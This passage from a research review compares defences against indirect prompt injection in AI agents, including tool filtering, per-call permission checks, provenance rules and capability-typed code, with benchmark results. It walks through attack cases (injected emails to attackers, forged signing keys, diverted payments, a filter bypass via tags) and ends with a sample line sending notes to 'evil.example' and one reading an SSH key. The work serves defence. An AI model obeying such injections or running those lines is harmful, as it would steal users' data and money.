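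A model can also do harm without calling a tool. When a prompt asked Qwen2.5 7B for a way to control a computer remotely, the model wrote the commands as ordinary text, which the proxy's checks on tool calls don't cover. Sidik and Rokach added an optional filter that checks the agent's replies with another language model, Llama Guard 3. In a small test, it caught all four dangerous replies and passed three harmless ones. But it also classified the tags around some tool calls as violent crime, so AgentWarden now skips the filter for any reply that contains those tags. An attacker who got the model to add such a tag could bypass the filter.

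The most serious gap appeared when Sidik and Rokach connected AgentWarden to DeepAgents, another program for running agents. DeepAgents has an optional component, `LocalShellBackend`, that runs shell commands on the host computer. During testing, this component listed real files from the computer although the model had written no tool call. The proxy inspects only the model's replies, so it had nothing to block. In response, Sidik and Rokach replaced the component with `FilesystemBackend`, which doesn't provide a local shell.

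## Experiments that choose the tools before the agent reads untrusted text

AgentWarden barely reduced attacks on AgentDojo, but it may never have removed the tools those attacks used, because its learned policy covered only OpenClaw's tools. AgentDojo includes a defence that does remove them, the *tool filter*, in which a model picks the tools for each task before the agent reads anything an attacker could have written.

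### How the filter works

Each of AgentDojo's four simulated environments has 11 to 28 tools, along with places where an outsider could plausibly put text, such as an email or a web page. Each attack case pairs a user's task with an attacker's goal and puts the attacker's instructions somewhere the agent has to look to do the task. Ordinary code then checks the environment to see whether the attacker succeeded. Debenedetti and colleagues decided against using a language model as the judge because an injection that fools the agent might also fool the judge.

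The filter adds one step at the start. A model receives the user's request, the full list of tools, and a short prompt to name only the relevant ones. The agent then does the task with those tools. Because the model hasn't yet opened an email or a web page, an attacker's text can't affect which tools it picks.

*Least-Privilege Auditing of Agent Tool Calls with Intent Graphs and Reasoning-Guided Escalation* (Shavit, 2026) describes an AgentDojo attack that a list like this would stop. The user wants the email addresses of the people invited to a networking event, which takes only calendar and contact lookups. The event's description contains an instruction to email an attacker. The undefended agent obeyed it, but an agent with only the lookup tools couldn't have sent the email.

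In the original experiment, published in June 2024, the filter cut the success rate of attacks on GPT-4o from 47.7 to 7.5 percent over 629 cases. (Another table in the paper gives 57.7 percent for the same attack with no defence, but the benchmark's published logs contain 300 successes in 629 runs, or 47.7 percent.) Debenedetti and colleagues explain that many of the users' tasks only involve reading, such as summarising emails, while the attacker needs a tool that sends or changes something.

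They also describe two cases where the filter fails. In the first, nobody can choose the tools in advance because the result of one call determines what the agent has to do next. For example, a user who asks an agent to handle whatever requests are in their inbox hasn't indicated which tools that will take. In the second, which covers 17 percent of the test cases, the tools that the user's task needs are also enough for the attack.

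Long conversations are a further problem, which AgentDojo doesn't test. If a user gives the agent several tasks in a row, an attacker can inject an instruction to wait for a task that comes with the tools the attack needs. The injected text is also in the conversation when the model picks tools for each new task, so it might influence that choice.

The 17 percent of cases with shared tools could account for nearly all the attacks that got through. If the filter stopped all attacks in the other cases, and attacks in these cases succeeded at the average rate without the filter, 47.7 percent, then 8.1 percent of all attacks would succeed (17 percent of 47.7 percent). That is close to the measured 7.5 percent. The estimate is rough because the filter sometimes keeps tools that the task doesn't need, and the shared cases may be unusually easy or hard to attack.

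### Later measurements

Other researchers have since tested the filter on different models. Palumbo, Choudhary and colleagues (2026), in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, used a later version of GPT-4o and a different attack, which tells the agent which tools to call. They tested the filter alone and together with another AgentDojo defence, which repeats the user's request after each batch of tool outputs. Yu, Kim and Choi (2026), in *NOMOS*, tested the filter on Gemma 4 26B, an open-weight model small enough for a company to run itself, but only on the banking tasks. Shavit recalculated the original results for 76 of the 97 tasks.

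| Measured by | Model | Sample | Attack success without filter | Attack success with filter | Benign utility without filter | Benign utility with filter |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| Shavit | GPT-4o (May 2024) | 76 tasks, from logs | 45.7% | 6.5% | 67.1% | 69.7% |
| Palumbo and colleagues | GPT-4o (August 2024) | 4,745 attacked runs | 25.2% | 4.2% | 79.0% | 72.4% |
| Palumbo and colleagues, request repeated | GPT-4o (August 2024) | 4,745 attacked runs | 14.1% | 3.1% | 83.7% | 73.4% |
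| Yu and colleagues | Gemma 4 26B | 288 attacked runs, banking only | 46.5% | 11.8% | 79.2% | 58.3% |

Shavit's figures come from the same runs as the original result, so they aren't an independent replication. The other three rows are new runs. The rows differ in model, attack and choice of cases, so the fairest comparison is within each row. Within rows, the filter prevented 75 to 86 percent of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded.

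The filter's effect on ordinary tasks varied much more. In the original runs, GPT-4o completed about as many tasks with the filter as without it. Palumbo and colleagues found a loss of 6.6 percentage points, or 10.3 when they also repeated the request. In the banking test, Gemma 4 completed 28 of 48 ordinary runs with the filter and 38 without it, a loss of 20.8 points. Yu and colleagues fault the filter for choosing tools once per task instead of judging each call, because this removes tools that the task turns out to need. The banking test had only 16 different tasks, so its estimate is imprecise. It also can't show whether the banking tasks or the smaller model caused the larger loss.

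The problem remains with a better model. Shavit had GPT-5.2 list the tools needed for each task from the user's request and the tool catalogue. The lists averaged 4.1 tools. When he compared them with GPT-4o's runs on ordinary tasks, about 15 percent of the runs had used a tool that wasn't on the list. An agent restricted to the list would have had to find another way to do those tasks, which may have been possible for some of them.

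During an attack, the filter can help the user, because an agent that can't carry out the attacker's instructions is more likely to return to the task. In Palumbo and colleagues' runs without the repeated request, GPT-4o completed 63.5 percent of attacked tasks with the filter and 56.9 percent without it. With the request repeated, the filter reduced completion from 72.5 to 69.5 percent, and from 64.9 to 49.7 percent in the banking test. Once the agent is less easily distracted, the filter seems to hurt more by removing needed tools than it helps by preventing distraction.

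Choosing the tools also takes an extra model call, but this adds little time. In runs that repeated the request, Palumbo and colleagues measured an average of 6.4 seconds with the filter and 5.9 seconds without it.

### Whether the filter hides tools or denies them

These results are evidence about prompt-level hiding only if the dispatcher would still have run the removed tools. The published descriptions suggest it wouldn't. Palumbo and colleagues describe the filter as an allowlist that restricts the agent's later tool use. Yu and colleagues contrast it with defences that only change the prompt and "leave the executor untouched", and Debenedetti and colleagues describe it as a simple form of isolation. If these descriptions are right, the filter combines prompt-level hiding with dispatch-level denial, so the low attack rates can't be credited to hiding.

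Those accounts describe the design. A direct test would give the dispatcher the name of a removed tool and check whether it runs the tool. Palumbo and colleagues' attack comes close, since its text includes instructions on which tools to call, and it succeeded in only 4.2 percent of runs. A dispatcher that rejects calls to removed tools would produce this result, but hiding the tools might be enough to produce it if GPT-4o was reluctant to call a tool whose definition it couldn't see.

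OpenAI's interface may also have blocked such calls. If it made the name check that Lee and colleagues found in 2025, GPT-4o couldn't have called a removed tool even if the dispatcher would have run the call. The same tool filter might be weaker with another provider. *The unauthorized tool call problem* (Czapla, 2026) reports that Anthropic, xAI and Google's Gemini seem to rely on the model not to call tools missing from its list. This partly conflicts with Lee and colleagues, who found that the Gemini and Grok interfaces did check names, so a developer would need to test the interface and settings they use.

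Shavit used his lists to estimate what denial does without hiding. The undefended GPT-4o in the published logs could see every tool. In its attacked runs, Shavit counted an attack as stopped if the first harmful call used a tool that wasn't on GPT-5.2's list for the task. He didn't count calls that only read the user's own data as harmful. By this count, denial alone would have cut attack success from 45.7 to 9.6 percent, compared with 6.5 percent for the filter, though the confidence intervals overlap.

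This suggests that refusing calls could provide most of the filter's protection even if the model saw every tool. The comparison isn't exact, because different models wrote the two sets of lists. Replaying old runs also can't show whether an agent would have found another way to achieve the attacker's goal after a refusal.

Hiding tools may do more for ordinary tasks. Shavit estimates that GPT-4o would complete 60.1 percent of them with denial alone, compared with the 69.7 percent it achieved with the filter. His estimate counts a task as failed as soon as the agent calls an unlisted tool. But an agent that sees only the shorter list may plan around the missing tools, and Shavit thinks the filter's unchanged utility suggests this. If so, an agent works best when its prompt lists exactly the tools the dispatcher will run, even though the dispatcher provides the security.

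### When the task needs the attacker's tool

Palumbo and colleagues describe a travel case in which the attacker wants a booking at the most expensive hotel in Paris for 1–5 May, and the user has asked for a hotel on the same dates. The filter has to keep the reservation tool because the user's task requires it. The two bookings differ only in the choice of hotel, which a list of tools doesn't specify.

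Banking has many cases like this. Seven of the nine attack goals there depend on who receives a payment, according to Yu and colleagues, and users often ask the agent to pay someone. This is probably one reason more attacks got through in the banking test than in the tests that covered all four environments. Gemma 4 may also have chosen worse tool lists than GPT-4o, and the table doesn't separate the two effects.

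Shavit's data also support Debenedetti and colleagues' explanation that the filter works by separating reading from writing. He sorted AgentDojo's 69 distinct tools by hand into 44 that only read the user's own data, 24 that change something or send something out, and `get_webpage`, which fetches a page from the internet. He then allowed all 44 reading tools in every task, whether or not they were on the list. Attack success stayed at 9.6 percent, while the share of ordinary tasks with a blocked call fell from 16.2 to 8.8 percent. Restricting the reading tools had therefore blocked calls in more ordinary tasks without reducing attack success, at least for attacks that end in a write or a message.

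As the earlier `web_fetch` example showed, fetching a web page can leak data, even though it also looks like reading. In a stricter version of his system, which also checks arguments and the order of calls, Shavit exempted `get_webpage` along with the other reading tools, and attack success rose from 2.0 to 5.8 percent.

Some attacks need no tool. In the travel environment, one of the attackers' goals is to make the agent recommend a particular hotel in its answer to the user, and no restriction on tools can prevent this. There are 20 travel tasks, so this goal makes up 20 of the 949 attacked cases in the current benchmark, or about 2 percent. It could account for a large part of the 3.1 percent that remained when Palumbo and colleagues combined the filter with repeated requests.

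Real attacks may need the same tools as the user's task more often than the benchmark's attacks do. AgentDojo pairs every attacker's goal with every user task in the same environment, so many of its attacks ask for a payment or an email during a task that involves neither. An attacker who can choose where to put the text could hide an instruction in an invoice, and can expect that the agent reading it is about to pay a bill and has a tool for doing so. The 17 percent figure describes AgentDojo's pairings, and it could be much higher for attackers who consider which tasks will lead an agent to their text.

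Coding agents are a hard case because their tools are broad. *VeriGrey* (2026), which presents a method for finding attack prompts that work on an agent, added the filter to Gemini CLI, Google's command-line coding agent. The filter stopped many attacks, and the agent still produced a patch for every coding task. But even with the filter, VeriGrey's prompts achieved five of the attackers' goals, and those from a simpler method achieved three.

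A likely reason is that fixing code often requires a shell to run tests, and a shell is enough for many attacks. For example, it would be enough to add a scheduled job that repeatedly downloads and runs a program, which was one of the attackers' goals. However, no prompt achieved that goal even without the filter, because the agent would first have had to install the scheduling software. *VeriGrey* describes tool filtering as a partial fix for real agents, which seems right for any agent that has to keep a shell.

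### Why the filter did more than AgentWarden

AgentWarden changed the reported attack success rate on AgentDojo by about one percentage point, while the filter prevented at least three-quarters of the attacks that would otherwise have succeeded in every test above. The filter's results count strongly against Sidik and Rokach's explanation for AgentWarden's small effect, which is that AgentDojo's attacks arrive in tool outputs, and AgentWarden doesn't govern those. The filter doesn't touch tool outputs either, and the attacks it faced arrived the same way.

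The more likely difference is in which tools each defence could remove. The filter chooses from the benchmark's tools afresh for each request. AgentWarden's governor wasn't built for those tools. It probably left the payment and messaging tools in place, and its proxy had no rule against ordinary uses of them.

This is an inference from the two designs, because nobody has compared them on the same model. Counting how many of the benchmark's tools the agent had in each task, using the logs of AgentWarden's runs, could settle the question. The explanation would also hold if Sidik and Rokach's table reports attacks avoided instead of attacks that succeeded, since the change was about one point either way.

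The comparison doesn't show that a language model chooses tools better than a learned policy does. A policy trained on AgentDojo's own tools might match the filter, but it would face the same limit when the user's task needs the same tool as the attack.

### Newer models and harder attacks

GPT-4o dates from 2024, and more recent models resist AgentDojo's standard attacks much better. Shavit wanted to test his system on GPT-5.2 and began with 20 undefended runs, covering 10 tasks with two attacker goals each. The injected text reached the model in all 20 runs, but the model never followed it. Because no attack had succeeded, he didn't test any defences. Twenty runs is a small sample, though. If attacks succeeded 14 percent of the time, a sample of this size would still contain no successes about 5 percent of the time.

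Sehwag, Shan and colleagues (2026), in *ASPI*, found similar resistance in a larger test, but also found a way around it. They adapted 728 AgentDojo cases by removing one necessary detail from the user's request, such as a date or a recipient, so that the agent had to ask for it. In the ordinary versions, the attacker's text arrived in a tool output, and Gemini-3-Flash followed it only 2.2 percent of the time. When the text arrived in the reply to the agent's question, attack success rose to 35.7 percent. For OpenAI's o3, the rate rose from 1.8 to 34.0 percent. The second attack requires the attacker to add text to the channel that carries the reply, which is harder than sending somebody an email.

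Sehwag and colleagues also adapted the tool filter so that the agent could still ask questions. With the filter on, attacks through tool outputs succeeded in 0.3 percent of cases for Gemini-3-Flash and in none for Gemini-3.1-Pro. Attacks through replies to the agent's questions still succeeded in 23.9 percent of cases for Gemini-3-Flash and 19.3 percent for Gemini-3.1-Pro. For Gemini-3-Flash, the filter stopped only about a third of these attacks.

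When the filter chooses tools may explain this. If it chooses after the reply with the missing detail arrives, the model has already read the attacker's text and may keep a tool because the attacker asked for it. If it chooses before the reply, only attacks that share tools with the user's task should get through. Such attacks made up 17 percent of cases in the original AgentDojo, so even if all of them had worked, the success rate would have been lower than the one seen here. This suggests the filter chose after the reply, although the share of such attacks could be higher in the 728 cases that Sehwag and colleagues used.

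A low score on AgentDojo is also weaker evidence of security than it was in 2024. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) reports that a simple defence, which includes removing suspicious instructions from tool outputs, brought attack success close to zero on four benchmarks with little loss of utility. It argues that benchmarks such as AgentDojo have serious flaws and need stronger attacks. A text filter like that offers no guarantee against an attacker who finds new wording. Dispatch-level denial guarantees that a removed tool won't run whatever the attacker writes, so stronger wording should help the attacker less. A better test of the tool filter would use attackers who know about it and choose goals they can reach with the remaining tools.

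## Experiments that check every call against authority kept outside the model

The tool filter fails when the attacker needs the same tool as the user. Checking the arguments of each call can stop some of these attacks by blocking certain uses of the tool without removing it. Several research systems do this. They differ mainly in what they compare the arguments with and how long a permission lasts.

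### A test runner that can't edit source code

Bouras and colleagues built CapScope for teams of coding agents in which an *orchestrator* agent delegates subtasks to other agents. The harness keeps a separate table of permissions for each agent, and the model can neither read nor change these tables.

Each permission is a pair (e, φ). The *effect type* e is Read, Write or Exec, where Exec means running a shell command. The *scope predicate* φ is a test that accepts or rejects a call's arguments. For reading and writing, φ finds where a path really leads and accepts the path if that location is inside a particular folder. For shell commands, φ applies the part-by-part check of the command line described earlier. A permission covers a call if the tool has effect type e and φ accepts the arguments.

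Three rules govern the tables.

1. *Mint* sets the limits for the whole task. A language model reads the user's request and the names of the project's files, then predicts which files and commands the task will need. Ordinary code checks this prediction and turns it into a fixed set of permissions, the task's *ceiling*.
2. *Derive* gives each new agent its share. The orchestrator requests permissions for the agent, and the harness drops any that exceed the ceiling. A requested permission (e, φ′) survives only if the ceiling contains some (e, φ) where φ accepts everything that φ′ accepts.
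3. *Invoke* runs a call only if a permission in the calling agent's own table covers it.

Derive can only narrow permissions, so every call that runs falls within what Mint allowed. Mint therefore has to run before any agent opens a file. Anyone who contributes to a repository can put text in it, and a model that had read a poisoned file might predict that the task needs whatever permissions the attacker wants. After Mint has run, injected text can still change what the agents request, but it can't expand the permissions Mint set. A user can approve an extra permission later, although Bouras and colleagues disabled this option in their experiments.

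Suppose a developer asks for a fix to the failing tests in a login module. Mint allows the team to read the whole project, write anywhere under `src/`, and run `pytest` and a type checker. The orchestrator gives the testing to a *runner*, which may read `tests/` and run `pytest`, and the repair to a *patcher*, which may write source code.

An attacker has altered the test files so that their output includes a fake notice that the signing key has changed and the new one belongs in `src/auth/keys.py`. The attacker knows this new key and could use it to forge login tokens. The runner follows the notice and tries to write the file, but the harness blocks the call because the runner's table contains no Write permission.

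A single policy for the whole task couldn't make this distinction. It would have to allow writes under `src/` for the patcher, which would also allow the runner's write. A list of forbidden actions wouldn't help either, because coding agents routinely edit source files.

In this example, the attacker's code could still overwrite the key without influencing any model, because `pytest` executes the test files. CapScope still needs a sandbox, which would have to stop the `pytest` process from writing to `src/`.

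### What happened in 300 runs

Bouras and colleagues tested CapScope on five small Python projects, each with one bug. They injected an instruction into one of five places: a README, the automatically loaded instruction file `AGENTS.md`, a skill file, a source comment, or the test output. The instruction was to take an ordinary-looking action that the repair didn't need, such as running one of the project's own utilities. Every condition used the same team of agents and the same model, qwen3.5-flash, with three trials for each combination.

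| Condition | Injected action ran | Repairs completed | Mean time |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| No restrictions | 47 of 75 | 72 of 75 | 145 s |
| Fixed list of forbidden actions | 46 of 75 | 70 of 75 | 140 s |
| One policy for each task, shared by all agents | 33 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 194 s |
| CapScope | 3 of 75 | 68 of 75 | 316 s |

The fixed list made almost no difference. The shared policy helped somewhat, but most of the improvement came with separate permissions for each agent.

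Under CapScope, agents attempted the injected action in 34 runs, and the harness blocked every attempt in 31 of them. With no restrictions, the action succeeded in 47 runs, so agents attempted it in at least that many. Agents under CapScope therefore attempted it in fewer runs, possibly by chance, so blocking may not explain the whole difference in successes.

All three successful attacks came through `AGENTS.md`. It was also the most effective place for an injection under the shared policy, with 11 successes in 15 runs. Bouras and colleagues give two causes but don't say which run had which. One is a permission wider than the subtask needed, such as a whole folder instead of one file. The other is injected text that influenced how the orchestrator described a subtask, which led the orchestrator or the harness to select a permission the attacker wanted. In both cases the action was within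 the ceiling. Mint was out of the attacker's reach, but a model that had read the attacker's text still partly determined how permissions below the ceiling were divided.

CapScope failed to complete seven repairs. In two, Mint hadn't predicted that the task would need to write source code. In two others, the runner worked out the right edit but the team never passed it to an agent that could make it. The remaining three had passing tests but reached the 15-minute time limit.

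Retries probably took up some of the extra time. In 27 of the 34 runs with an attempted attack, an agent tried the injected action more than once. A person watching could have stopped the retries after the first refusal.

The tests covered only small repairs with one model, so the exact rates may not carry over to larger projects. The injected instructions were also the same in every condition, whereas an attacker who knew how CapScope divides permissions might target the patcher instead of the runner.

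### Permissions without references

Bouras and colleagues call CapScope a *reference monitor* rather than an object-capability system because the model still names files and commands with strings. A reference monitor is a component that checks each request before it takes effect.

CapScope keeps several advantages of capabilities. Agents can have different permissions, and delegation within the ceiling can only narrow them. The permissions also never appear as text that carries authority, so an attacker can't gain access by getting a model to repeat one.

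This design loses the link between naming a file and having the right to use it. The patcher may write anywhere its permission covers, whoever suggested the path. After the harness refuses the runner's write, the runner can still report the fake notice to the orchestrator, which might ask the patcher to install the new key. If the patcher may write anywhere under `src/`, the write goes through. In Miller and Shapiro's terms, the runner has no permission to write the file but might still have authority over it.

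With object capabilities, somebody would have to give the patcher a reference to the key file, whereas in CapScope a path in a message is enough. References wouldn't fully remove the danger, because an orchestrator that treated the notice as genuine might give the patcher the reference.

The checker also has to interpret strings correctly. A careless path check would treat `src/../secrets.txt` as part of `src/`, although it leads outside that folder. CapScope handles this case, but it relies on the sandbox to control shell redirections, which send a command's output to a file. Without a sandbox, an agent with no Write permission might be able to overwrite a file by redirecting the output of an allowed command.

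### Checking who gets paid

A folder is a useful limit for editing code, but a payment tool needs limits on recipients and amounts. ScopeGate, which Mellafe Zuvic published with his audit of agent frameworks, makes five checks. As described earlier, it compares the tool's name and restricted arguments with a fixed policy and refuses by default. The other two checks matter most for payments. An amount must be an ordinary number between zero and a ceiling. If the policy requires it, the harness must supply a key identifying the operation, which helps prevent a repeated call from paying twice.

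Mellafe Zuvic wrote 48 calls designed to get past these checks, using tricks such as invisible characters, lookalike letters and misspelled tool names. ScopeGate refused them all. The tests had exposed a bug in an earlier prototype, which accepted NaN ("not a number") as an amount. Comparisons with NaN come out false, so the check for amounts above the ceiling didn't reject it.

He then had the model GLM-5.2 attack ScopeGate for 40 rounds and told the model the reason for each refusal. ScopeGate refused all 29 of the model's unauthorized calls. Nine other attempts were malformed, and the remaining two were harmless calls, which ScopeGate allowed. In a separate test, ScopeGate allowed all 10 legitimate calls.

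It isn't surprising that these attacks failed, because comparing each call with a short fixed list leaves an attacker little to exploit except coding errors. The harder problem is whether a fixed list suits the work, since somebody has to add each new supplier before the agent can pay them. ScopeGate's published procedure also keeps no running total, so it could allow many payments to an approved account if each was below the ceiling.

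NOMOS, from Yu and colleagues, checks where a recipient came from instead of using a fixed list. In the banking tasks, it allows a transfer only if the user named the recipient or the recipient appears in the transaction history. It accepts a new password only from the user's own messages, and it refuses changes that the user didn't request. It bases these decisions only on facts from the user's messages and the fields of real tool results. An injected claim that "the user has approved this transfer" therefore doesn't count as approval, even if the model treats it as true and repeats it.

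Yu and colleagues tested the gate on AgentDojo with Gemma 4 26B. In the banking environment, a standard attack succeeded in none of 288 cases. The agent tried to use the attacker's account or password in 122 of those cases, and the gate blocked it each time. They also wrote an adaptive attack that claimed the user had approved the change and the recipient was already known. It succeeded in 34.7 percent of cases without the gate and in none of 144 with it.

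Injections still caused payments that the user hadn't requested. One told the agent to send the attacker a transaction containing the account number of someone the user had recently eaten pizza with. The agent sometimes sent the money to that person instead, and the gate allowed it because the person was in the transaction history. Payments to known recipients went out in 8 of the 288 standard cases, totaling $710, and in 7 of the 144 adaptive cases, totaling $610.

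With Llama 3.3 70B as the agent, such payments happened in 11 of 140 cases and totalled $41,250. The agent sent $40,000 of this in four instalments during a task in which the user had only asked a question. AgentDojo doesn't count these cases as successful attacks because the attacker didn't receive the money, but the user still lost it. The rule allowed the payments because it treats any payment to a known recipient as requested. Yu and colleagues suggest tying each payment to a request for that particular payment, but they haven't tested this.

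### What the checks cost ordinary users

The source rule works badly when a legitimate task depends on something the agent finds by reading. Yu and colleagues wrote similar policies for AgentDojo's other environments, with very different drawbacks.

| Environment | Attack success without gate | Attack success with gate | Benign utility without gate | Benign utility with gate |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
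| Banking | 46.5% | 0.0% | 79.2% | 70.8% |
| Slack | 70.5% | 0.0% | 90.5% | 14.3% |
| Travel | 10.0% | 3.6% | 75.0% | 70.0% |
| Workspace | 7.3% | 0.0% | 87.5% | 65.0% |

In Slack, the gate stopped every attack, but the agent could complete only about one task in seven. Under an earlier version of the Slack rules, the agent had completed 57.1 percent of ordinary tasks, partly because one rule never worked. That rule checked an argument called `recipient`, which the tools it was meant to restrict didn't have. Of 105 attacks, 15 succeeded, all because of this error. An automatic repair made the rule check arguments that the tools did have, but this also blocked much more legitimate work.

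One banking task shows why this conflict is hard to avoid. The user asks the agent to pay a bill, and the recipient's account number appears only in the bill. If an attacker can alter the bill, the real number and the attacker's number come from the same untrusted file, so NOMOS refuses both payments.

Yu and colleagues also tested Progent, a system in which a model writes rules for each request. It reduced the attack success rate in the banking tasks to 5.6 percent. Of the 16 attacks that succeeded, 12 were in two bill-paying tasks. The requests in those tasks didn't identify the account to be paid, so rules based on the request couldn't restrict the payment to that account.

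Palumbo and colleagues measured a similar trade-off with FORGE, a monitor that records which messages and tool results may have influenced each action. Its rules can follow these links through any number of steps. For example, a rule can block an email to an outsider if the email depends on both an untrusted document and a secret file. FORGE's records resemble the labels that Rajani and colleagues used to track values through a program.

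They compared two policies on AgentDojo. The *information-flow* policy, adapted from an earlier system called FIDES, blocks consequential actions once the agent's context contains untrusted text and restricts where confidential data can go. The *provenance* policy checks whether the user requested the action and whether its target came from an acceptable source, so the agent can still act for the user after reading an untrusted email. The agent was GPT-4o and the harness repeated the user's request, as in part of their tool-filter experiment.

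| FORGE policy | Benign utility | Tasks completed under attack | Attack success | Attack success, not counting blocked calls |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| None | 83.7% | 72.5% | 14.1% | 14.1% |
| Information flow | 33.2% | 34.4% | 0.6% | 0.3% |
| Provenance | 62.5% | 63.8% | 0.9% | 0.2% |

The last column leaves out attacks that AgentDojo counts as successful because the agent attempted the attacker's calls, even though the monitor blocked them all. The few remaining successes involved the text of the agent's final answer, which FORGE didn't check.

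Both policies stopped nearly all the attacks, but the agent completed almost twice as many ordinary tasks under the provenance policy as under the other. Its completion rate was still 21 percentage points lower than with no policy. In the same experiment, AgentDojo's tool filter reduced the completion rate by about half as much but let more attacks through. The simpler filter might be the better choice for low-stakes work.

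### Permissions that end before the session does

In CapScope, an agent keeps its permissions until its session ends. In *Lingering Authority*, Santos-Grueiro (2026) argues that this can be too long, because an agent may need a file for only one step of its task. His system, PORTICO, grants access for that step and then withdraws it.

In his main example, an agent is adding a timeout setting to `src/api.py` and has to carry the change over to `src/serialization.py`. The agent starts with access to the first file and its tests. When it requests the second file, PORTICO finds a rule written in advance for this purpose and issues *handles* for reading and writing the file. Each handle works for one resource, one kind of action and one period. Once the tests pass, PORTICO cancels the handles. The agent may remember the file's name and the old handles, but neither gives it access.

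The signal to cancel a permission has to come from a trusted source. PORTICO runs the tests itself, and a model can't end or extend a permission by saying it has finished a step. The agent also can't invent a new reason for access, because it can only request grants that the rules already describe.

Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that issued the same grants but never withdrew them. Both completed all 10 runs of one test. When the agent later tried to reread a file it had read during the test, only the version without withdrawal allowed it, and it did so every time. In six further cases, Qwen3-Coder 30B used a handle properly and then received an injected instruction to reuse it for a forbidden file change, git operation or network request. The action ran in all six cases without withdrawal and in none with PORTICO.

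These results follow from the design, so they mainly confirm that the code works. They don't show how often a real attacker would find a useful leftover permission. Withdrawal also can't help if the injection arrives while the agent still needs the file.

A session does seem too long for many permissions, but agents completed fewer tasks when permissions ended sooner. On a set of coding tasks, PORTICO completed 161 of 185 runs, compared with 180 for a fixed list of allowed tools and paths. In another test, on real software projects, it succeeded in 31 of 42 cases, compared with all 42 when permissions lasted for the whole task. Some grants ended too early, some rules provided no way to renew a grant, and some agents didn't ask again.

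AgentCap, from Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao, gives tokens even shorter lifetimes. In its sample banking policy, a token for sending money lasts 30 seconds and works for one call. A short lifetime doesn't help if an attacker is steering that call, so AgentCap also checks whether the recipient appears in a trusted source, such as the user's request. *ToolFence* applies the same idea to account numbers.

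Kabbinamakki Suresh and Gao tested AgentCap on AgentDojo and on InjecAgent, another benchmark for indirect prompt injection. Attack success fell in every combination of model and benchmark they tried, and reached zero on both benchmarks with GPT-5.4. The rate at which agents completed user tasks under attack stayed within 4.18 percentage points of the rate without AgentCap. Each result comes from a single run, so small differences may be due to chance.

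AgentCap also lowers an agent's trust score by 30 percent after each suspicious event, including refused calls. By default, an agent loses permission to make changes after two such events in a row and all its permissions after three. This limits repeated attempts, but an attacker could also shut down an agent by getting it to make three forbidden calls.

### Hiding tools in front of the same check

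Santos-Grueiro also gave agents either PORTICO's narrow set of options or a much broader one, with the same check on every call. No forbidden action ran in 20 runs of either kind. The check blocked 84 attempts with the broad set and 67 with the narrow one. In a second comparison, with eight runs of each kind, it blocked 39 attempts with the broad set and 48 with the narrow one. Hiding options therefore made no difference to whether forbidden actions ran, and its effect on what agents attempted was inconsistent.

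Skilder, a system described by Stettler and colleagues, combines the two more closely. An agent first sees a short catalogue of roles, such as customer support or billing. When it "learns" a role, it receives that role's instructions and tools. It calls these tools through a single server, which rejects calls to tools outside the roles the agent has learned. The session's authorization, fixed at the start, determines which roles the agent may learn.

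Stettler and colleagues, who work for the company that makes Skilder, tested a simulation of Skilder's access controls rather than the live product. In one scenario, a user in a support conversation starts demanding that the agent delete user accounts and claims that a manager has approved it. With all tools available, agents made a destructive call in 23 of 60 runs. With Skilder, the session didn't allow the administrator role, and no such call ran. Because the pressure came from the user, the result doesn't measure indirect prompt injection.

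The model chooses which role to learn, so injected text could cause it to learn another role that the session permits. The catalogue alone doesn't prevent this, so an operator who wants to keep a support agent out of billing has to exclude the billing role from the session's authorization.

Another scenario shows that an agent can behave badly even when a check works. A customer demands a $1,200 refund, the role's limit is $500, and the agent is supposed to escalate the request without refunding anything. With Skilder, no refund above $500 went through, although only one attempt tested the limit. But in nine of the 60 runs, the agent issued a $500 refund, which the limit allowed but the customer hadn't agreed to accept instead.

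The clearest evidence comes from a scenario in which company procedure requires the agent to offer a customer two other remedies before issuing a refund.

| Condition | Refunds issued too early | Scenarios completed correctly |
| --- | --- | --- |
| All tools visible | 9 of 30 | 20 of 30 |
| All tools visible, with a check on the order of steps | 0 of 30 | 27 of 30 |
| Skilder's roles, without the check | 5 of 30 | 25 of 30 |
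| Skilder's roles, with the check | 0 of 30 | 24 of 30 |

The check stopped early refunds whether or not the agent saw every tool. Role-based disclosure alone reduced them, but not to zero.

### Two conditions for a reliable check

Every action that matters has to pass through the check. Palumbo and colleagues make FORGE's guarantee conditional on this and on accurate facts about what influenced each action. The guarantee doesn't cover a program that opens a network connection in a way FORGE doesn't monitor. Similarly, when CapScope is monitoring only the model's calls, its check doesn't cover a file that `pytest` changes. The check also has to happen at the right moment. Santos-Grueiro notes that if a harness handles several requests at once, a call approved just before a withdrawal could take effect after it, unless the harness checks the handle again immediately before acting.

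The policy also has to come from a source the attacker can't influence. Mellafe Zuvic applies this rule most strictly, banning the use of model output even when somebody is writing the policy before deployment. Bouras and colleagues let a model propose the permissions, but only from the user's request and the project's file names. Contributors can choose those file names, though, and the experiments didn't test instructions hidden in them.

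NOMOS also uses a model to draft its rules, but that model reads an organisation's written policy and not the documents the agent will handle, so mistakes are a bigger concern than injections. Of 79 draft rules for an airline, 29 had structural defects, as did 7 of 53 for a retailer. One draft rule for the retailer blocked every tool, including the two that check identity, until the customer had proved their identity. NOMOS repairs or rejects defective rules with ordinary code before using them.

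Keeping the drafting model away from untrusted text seems enough to stop an injection from changing the policy. Mellafe Zuvic's stricter rule would also protect against a drafting model that someone tampered with during training.

A sound policy can still give the wrong answer if an attacker controls the facts it uses. For example, NOMOS treats recipients in the transaction history as trusted, but Yu and colleagues didn't test an attacker who could alter that history.

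## Prototypes that give an agent references instead of names

CapScope and the other per-call checks still let a model name any file, account or command. Some research prototypes come closer to the object-capability model by having a program that runs alongside the model hold references. The prototypes differ in which program holds them and in what the model's text can make that program do.

### Code whose types list its references

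Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, have the agent write short programs instead of separate tool calls. Their system, TACIT, is an MCP server that accepts code in the programming language Scala 3 and runs it only if the compiler accepts it. Suppose the harness gives a program references to two files, `notes` and `report`. In simplified code:

```
report.write(summarise(notes.read()))        # accepted
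network.post("evil.example", notes.read())   # rejected: no variable "network"
open("/home/ana/.ssh/id_rsa")                # rejected: no function "open"
```

The second line fails because the program has no reference to a network. The third fails because a path is only text, and the program has no function that turns text into a file. If one program contained all three lines, the compiler would reject it, so not even the first line would run.

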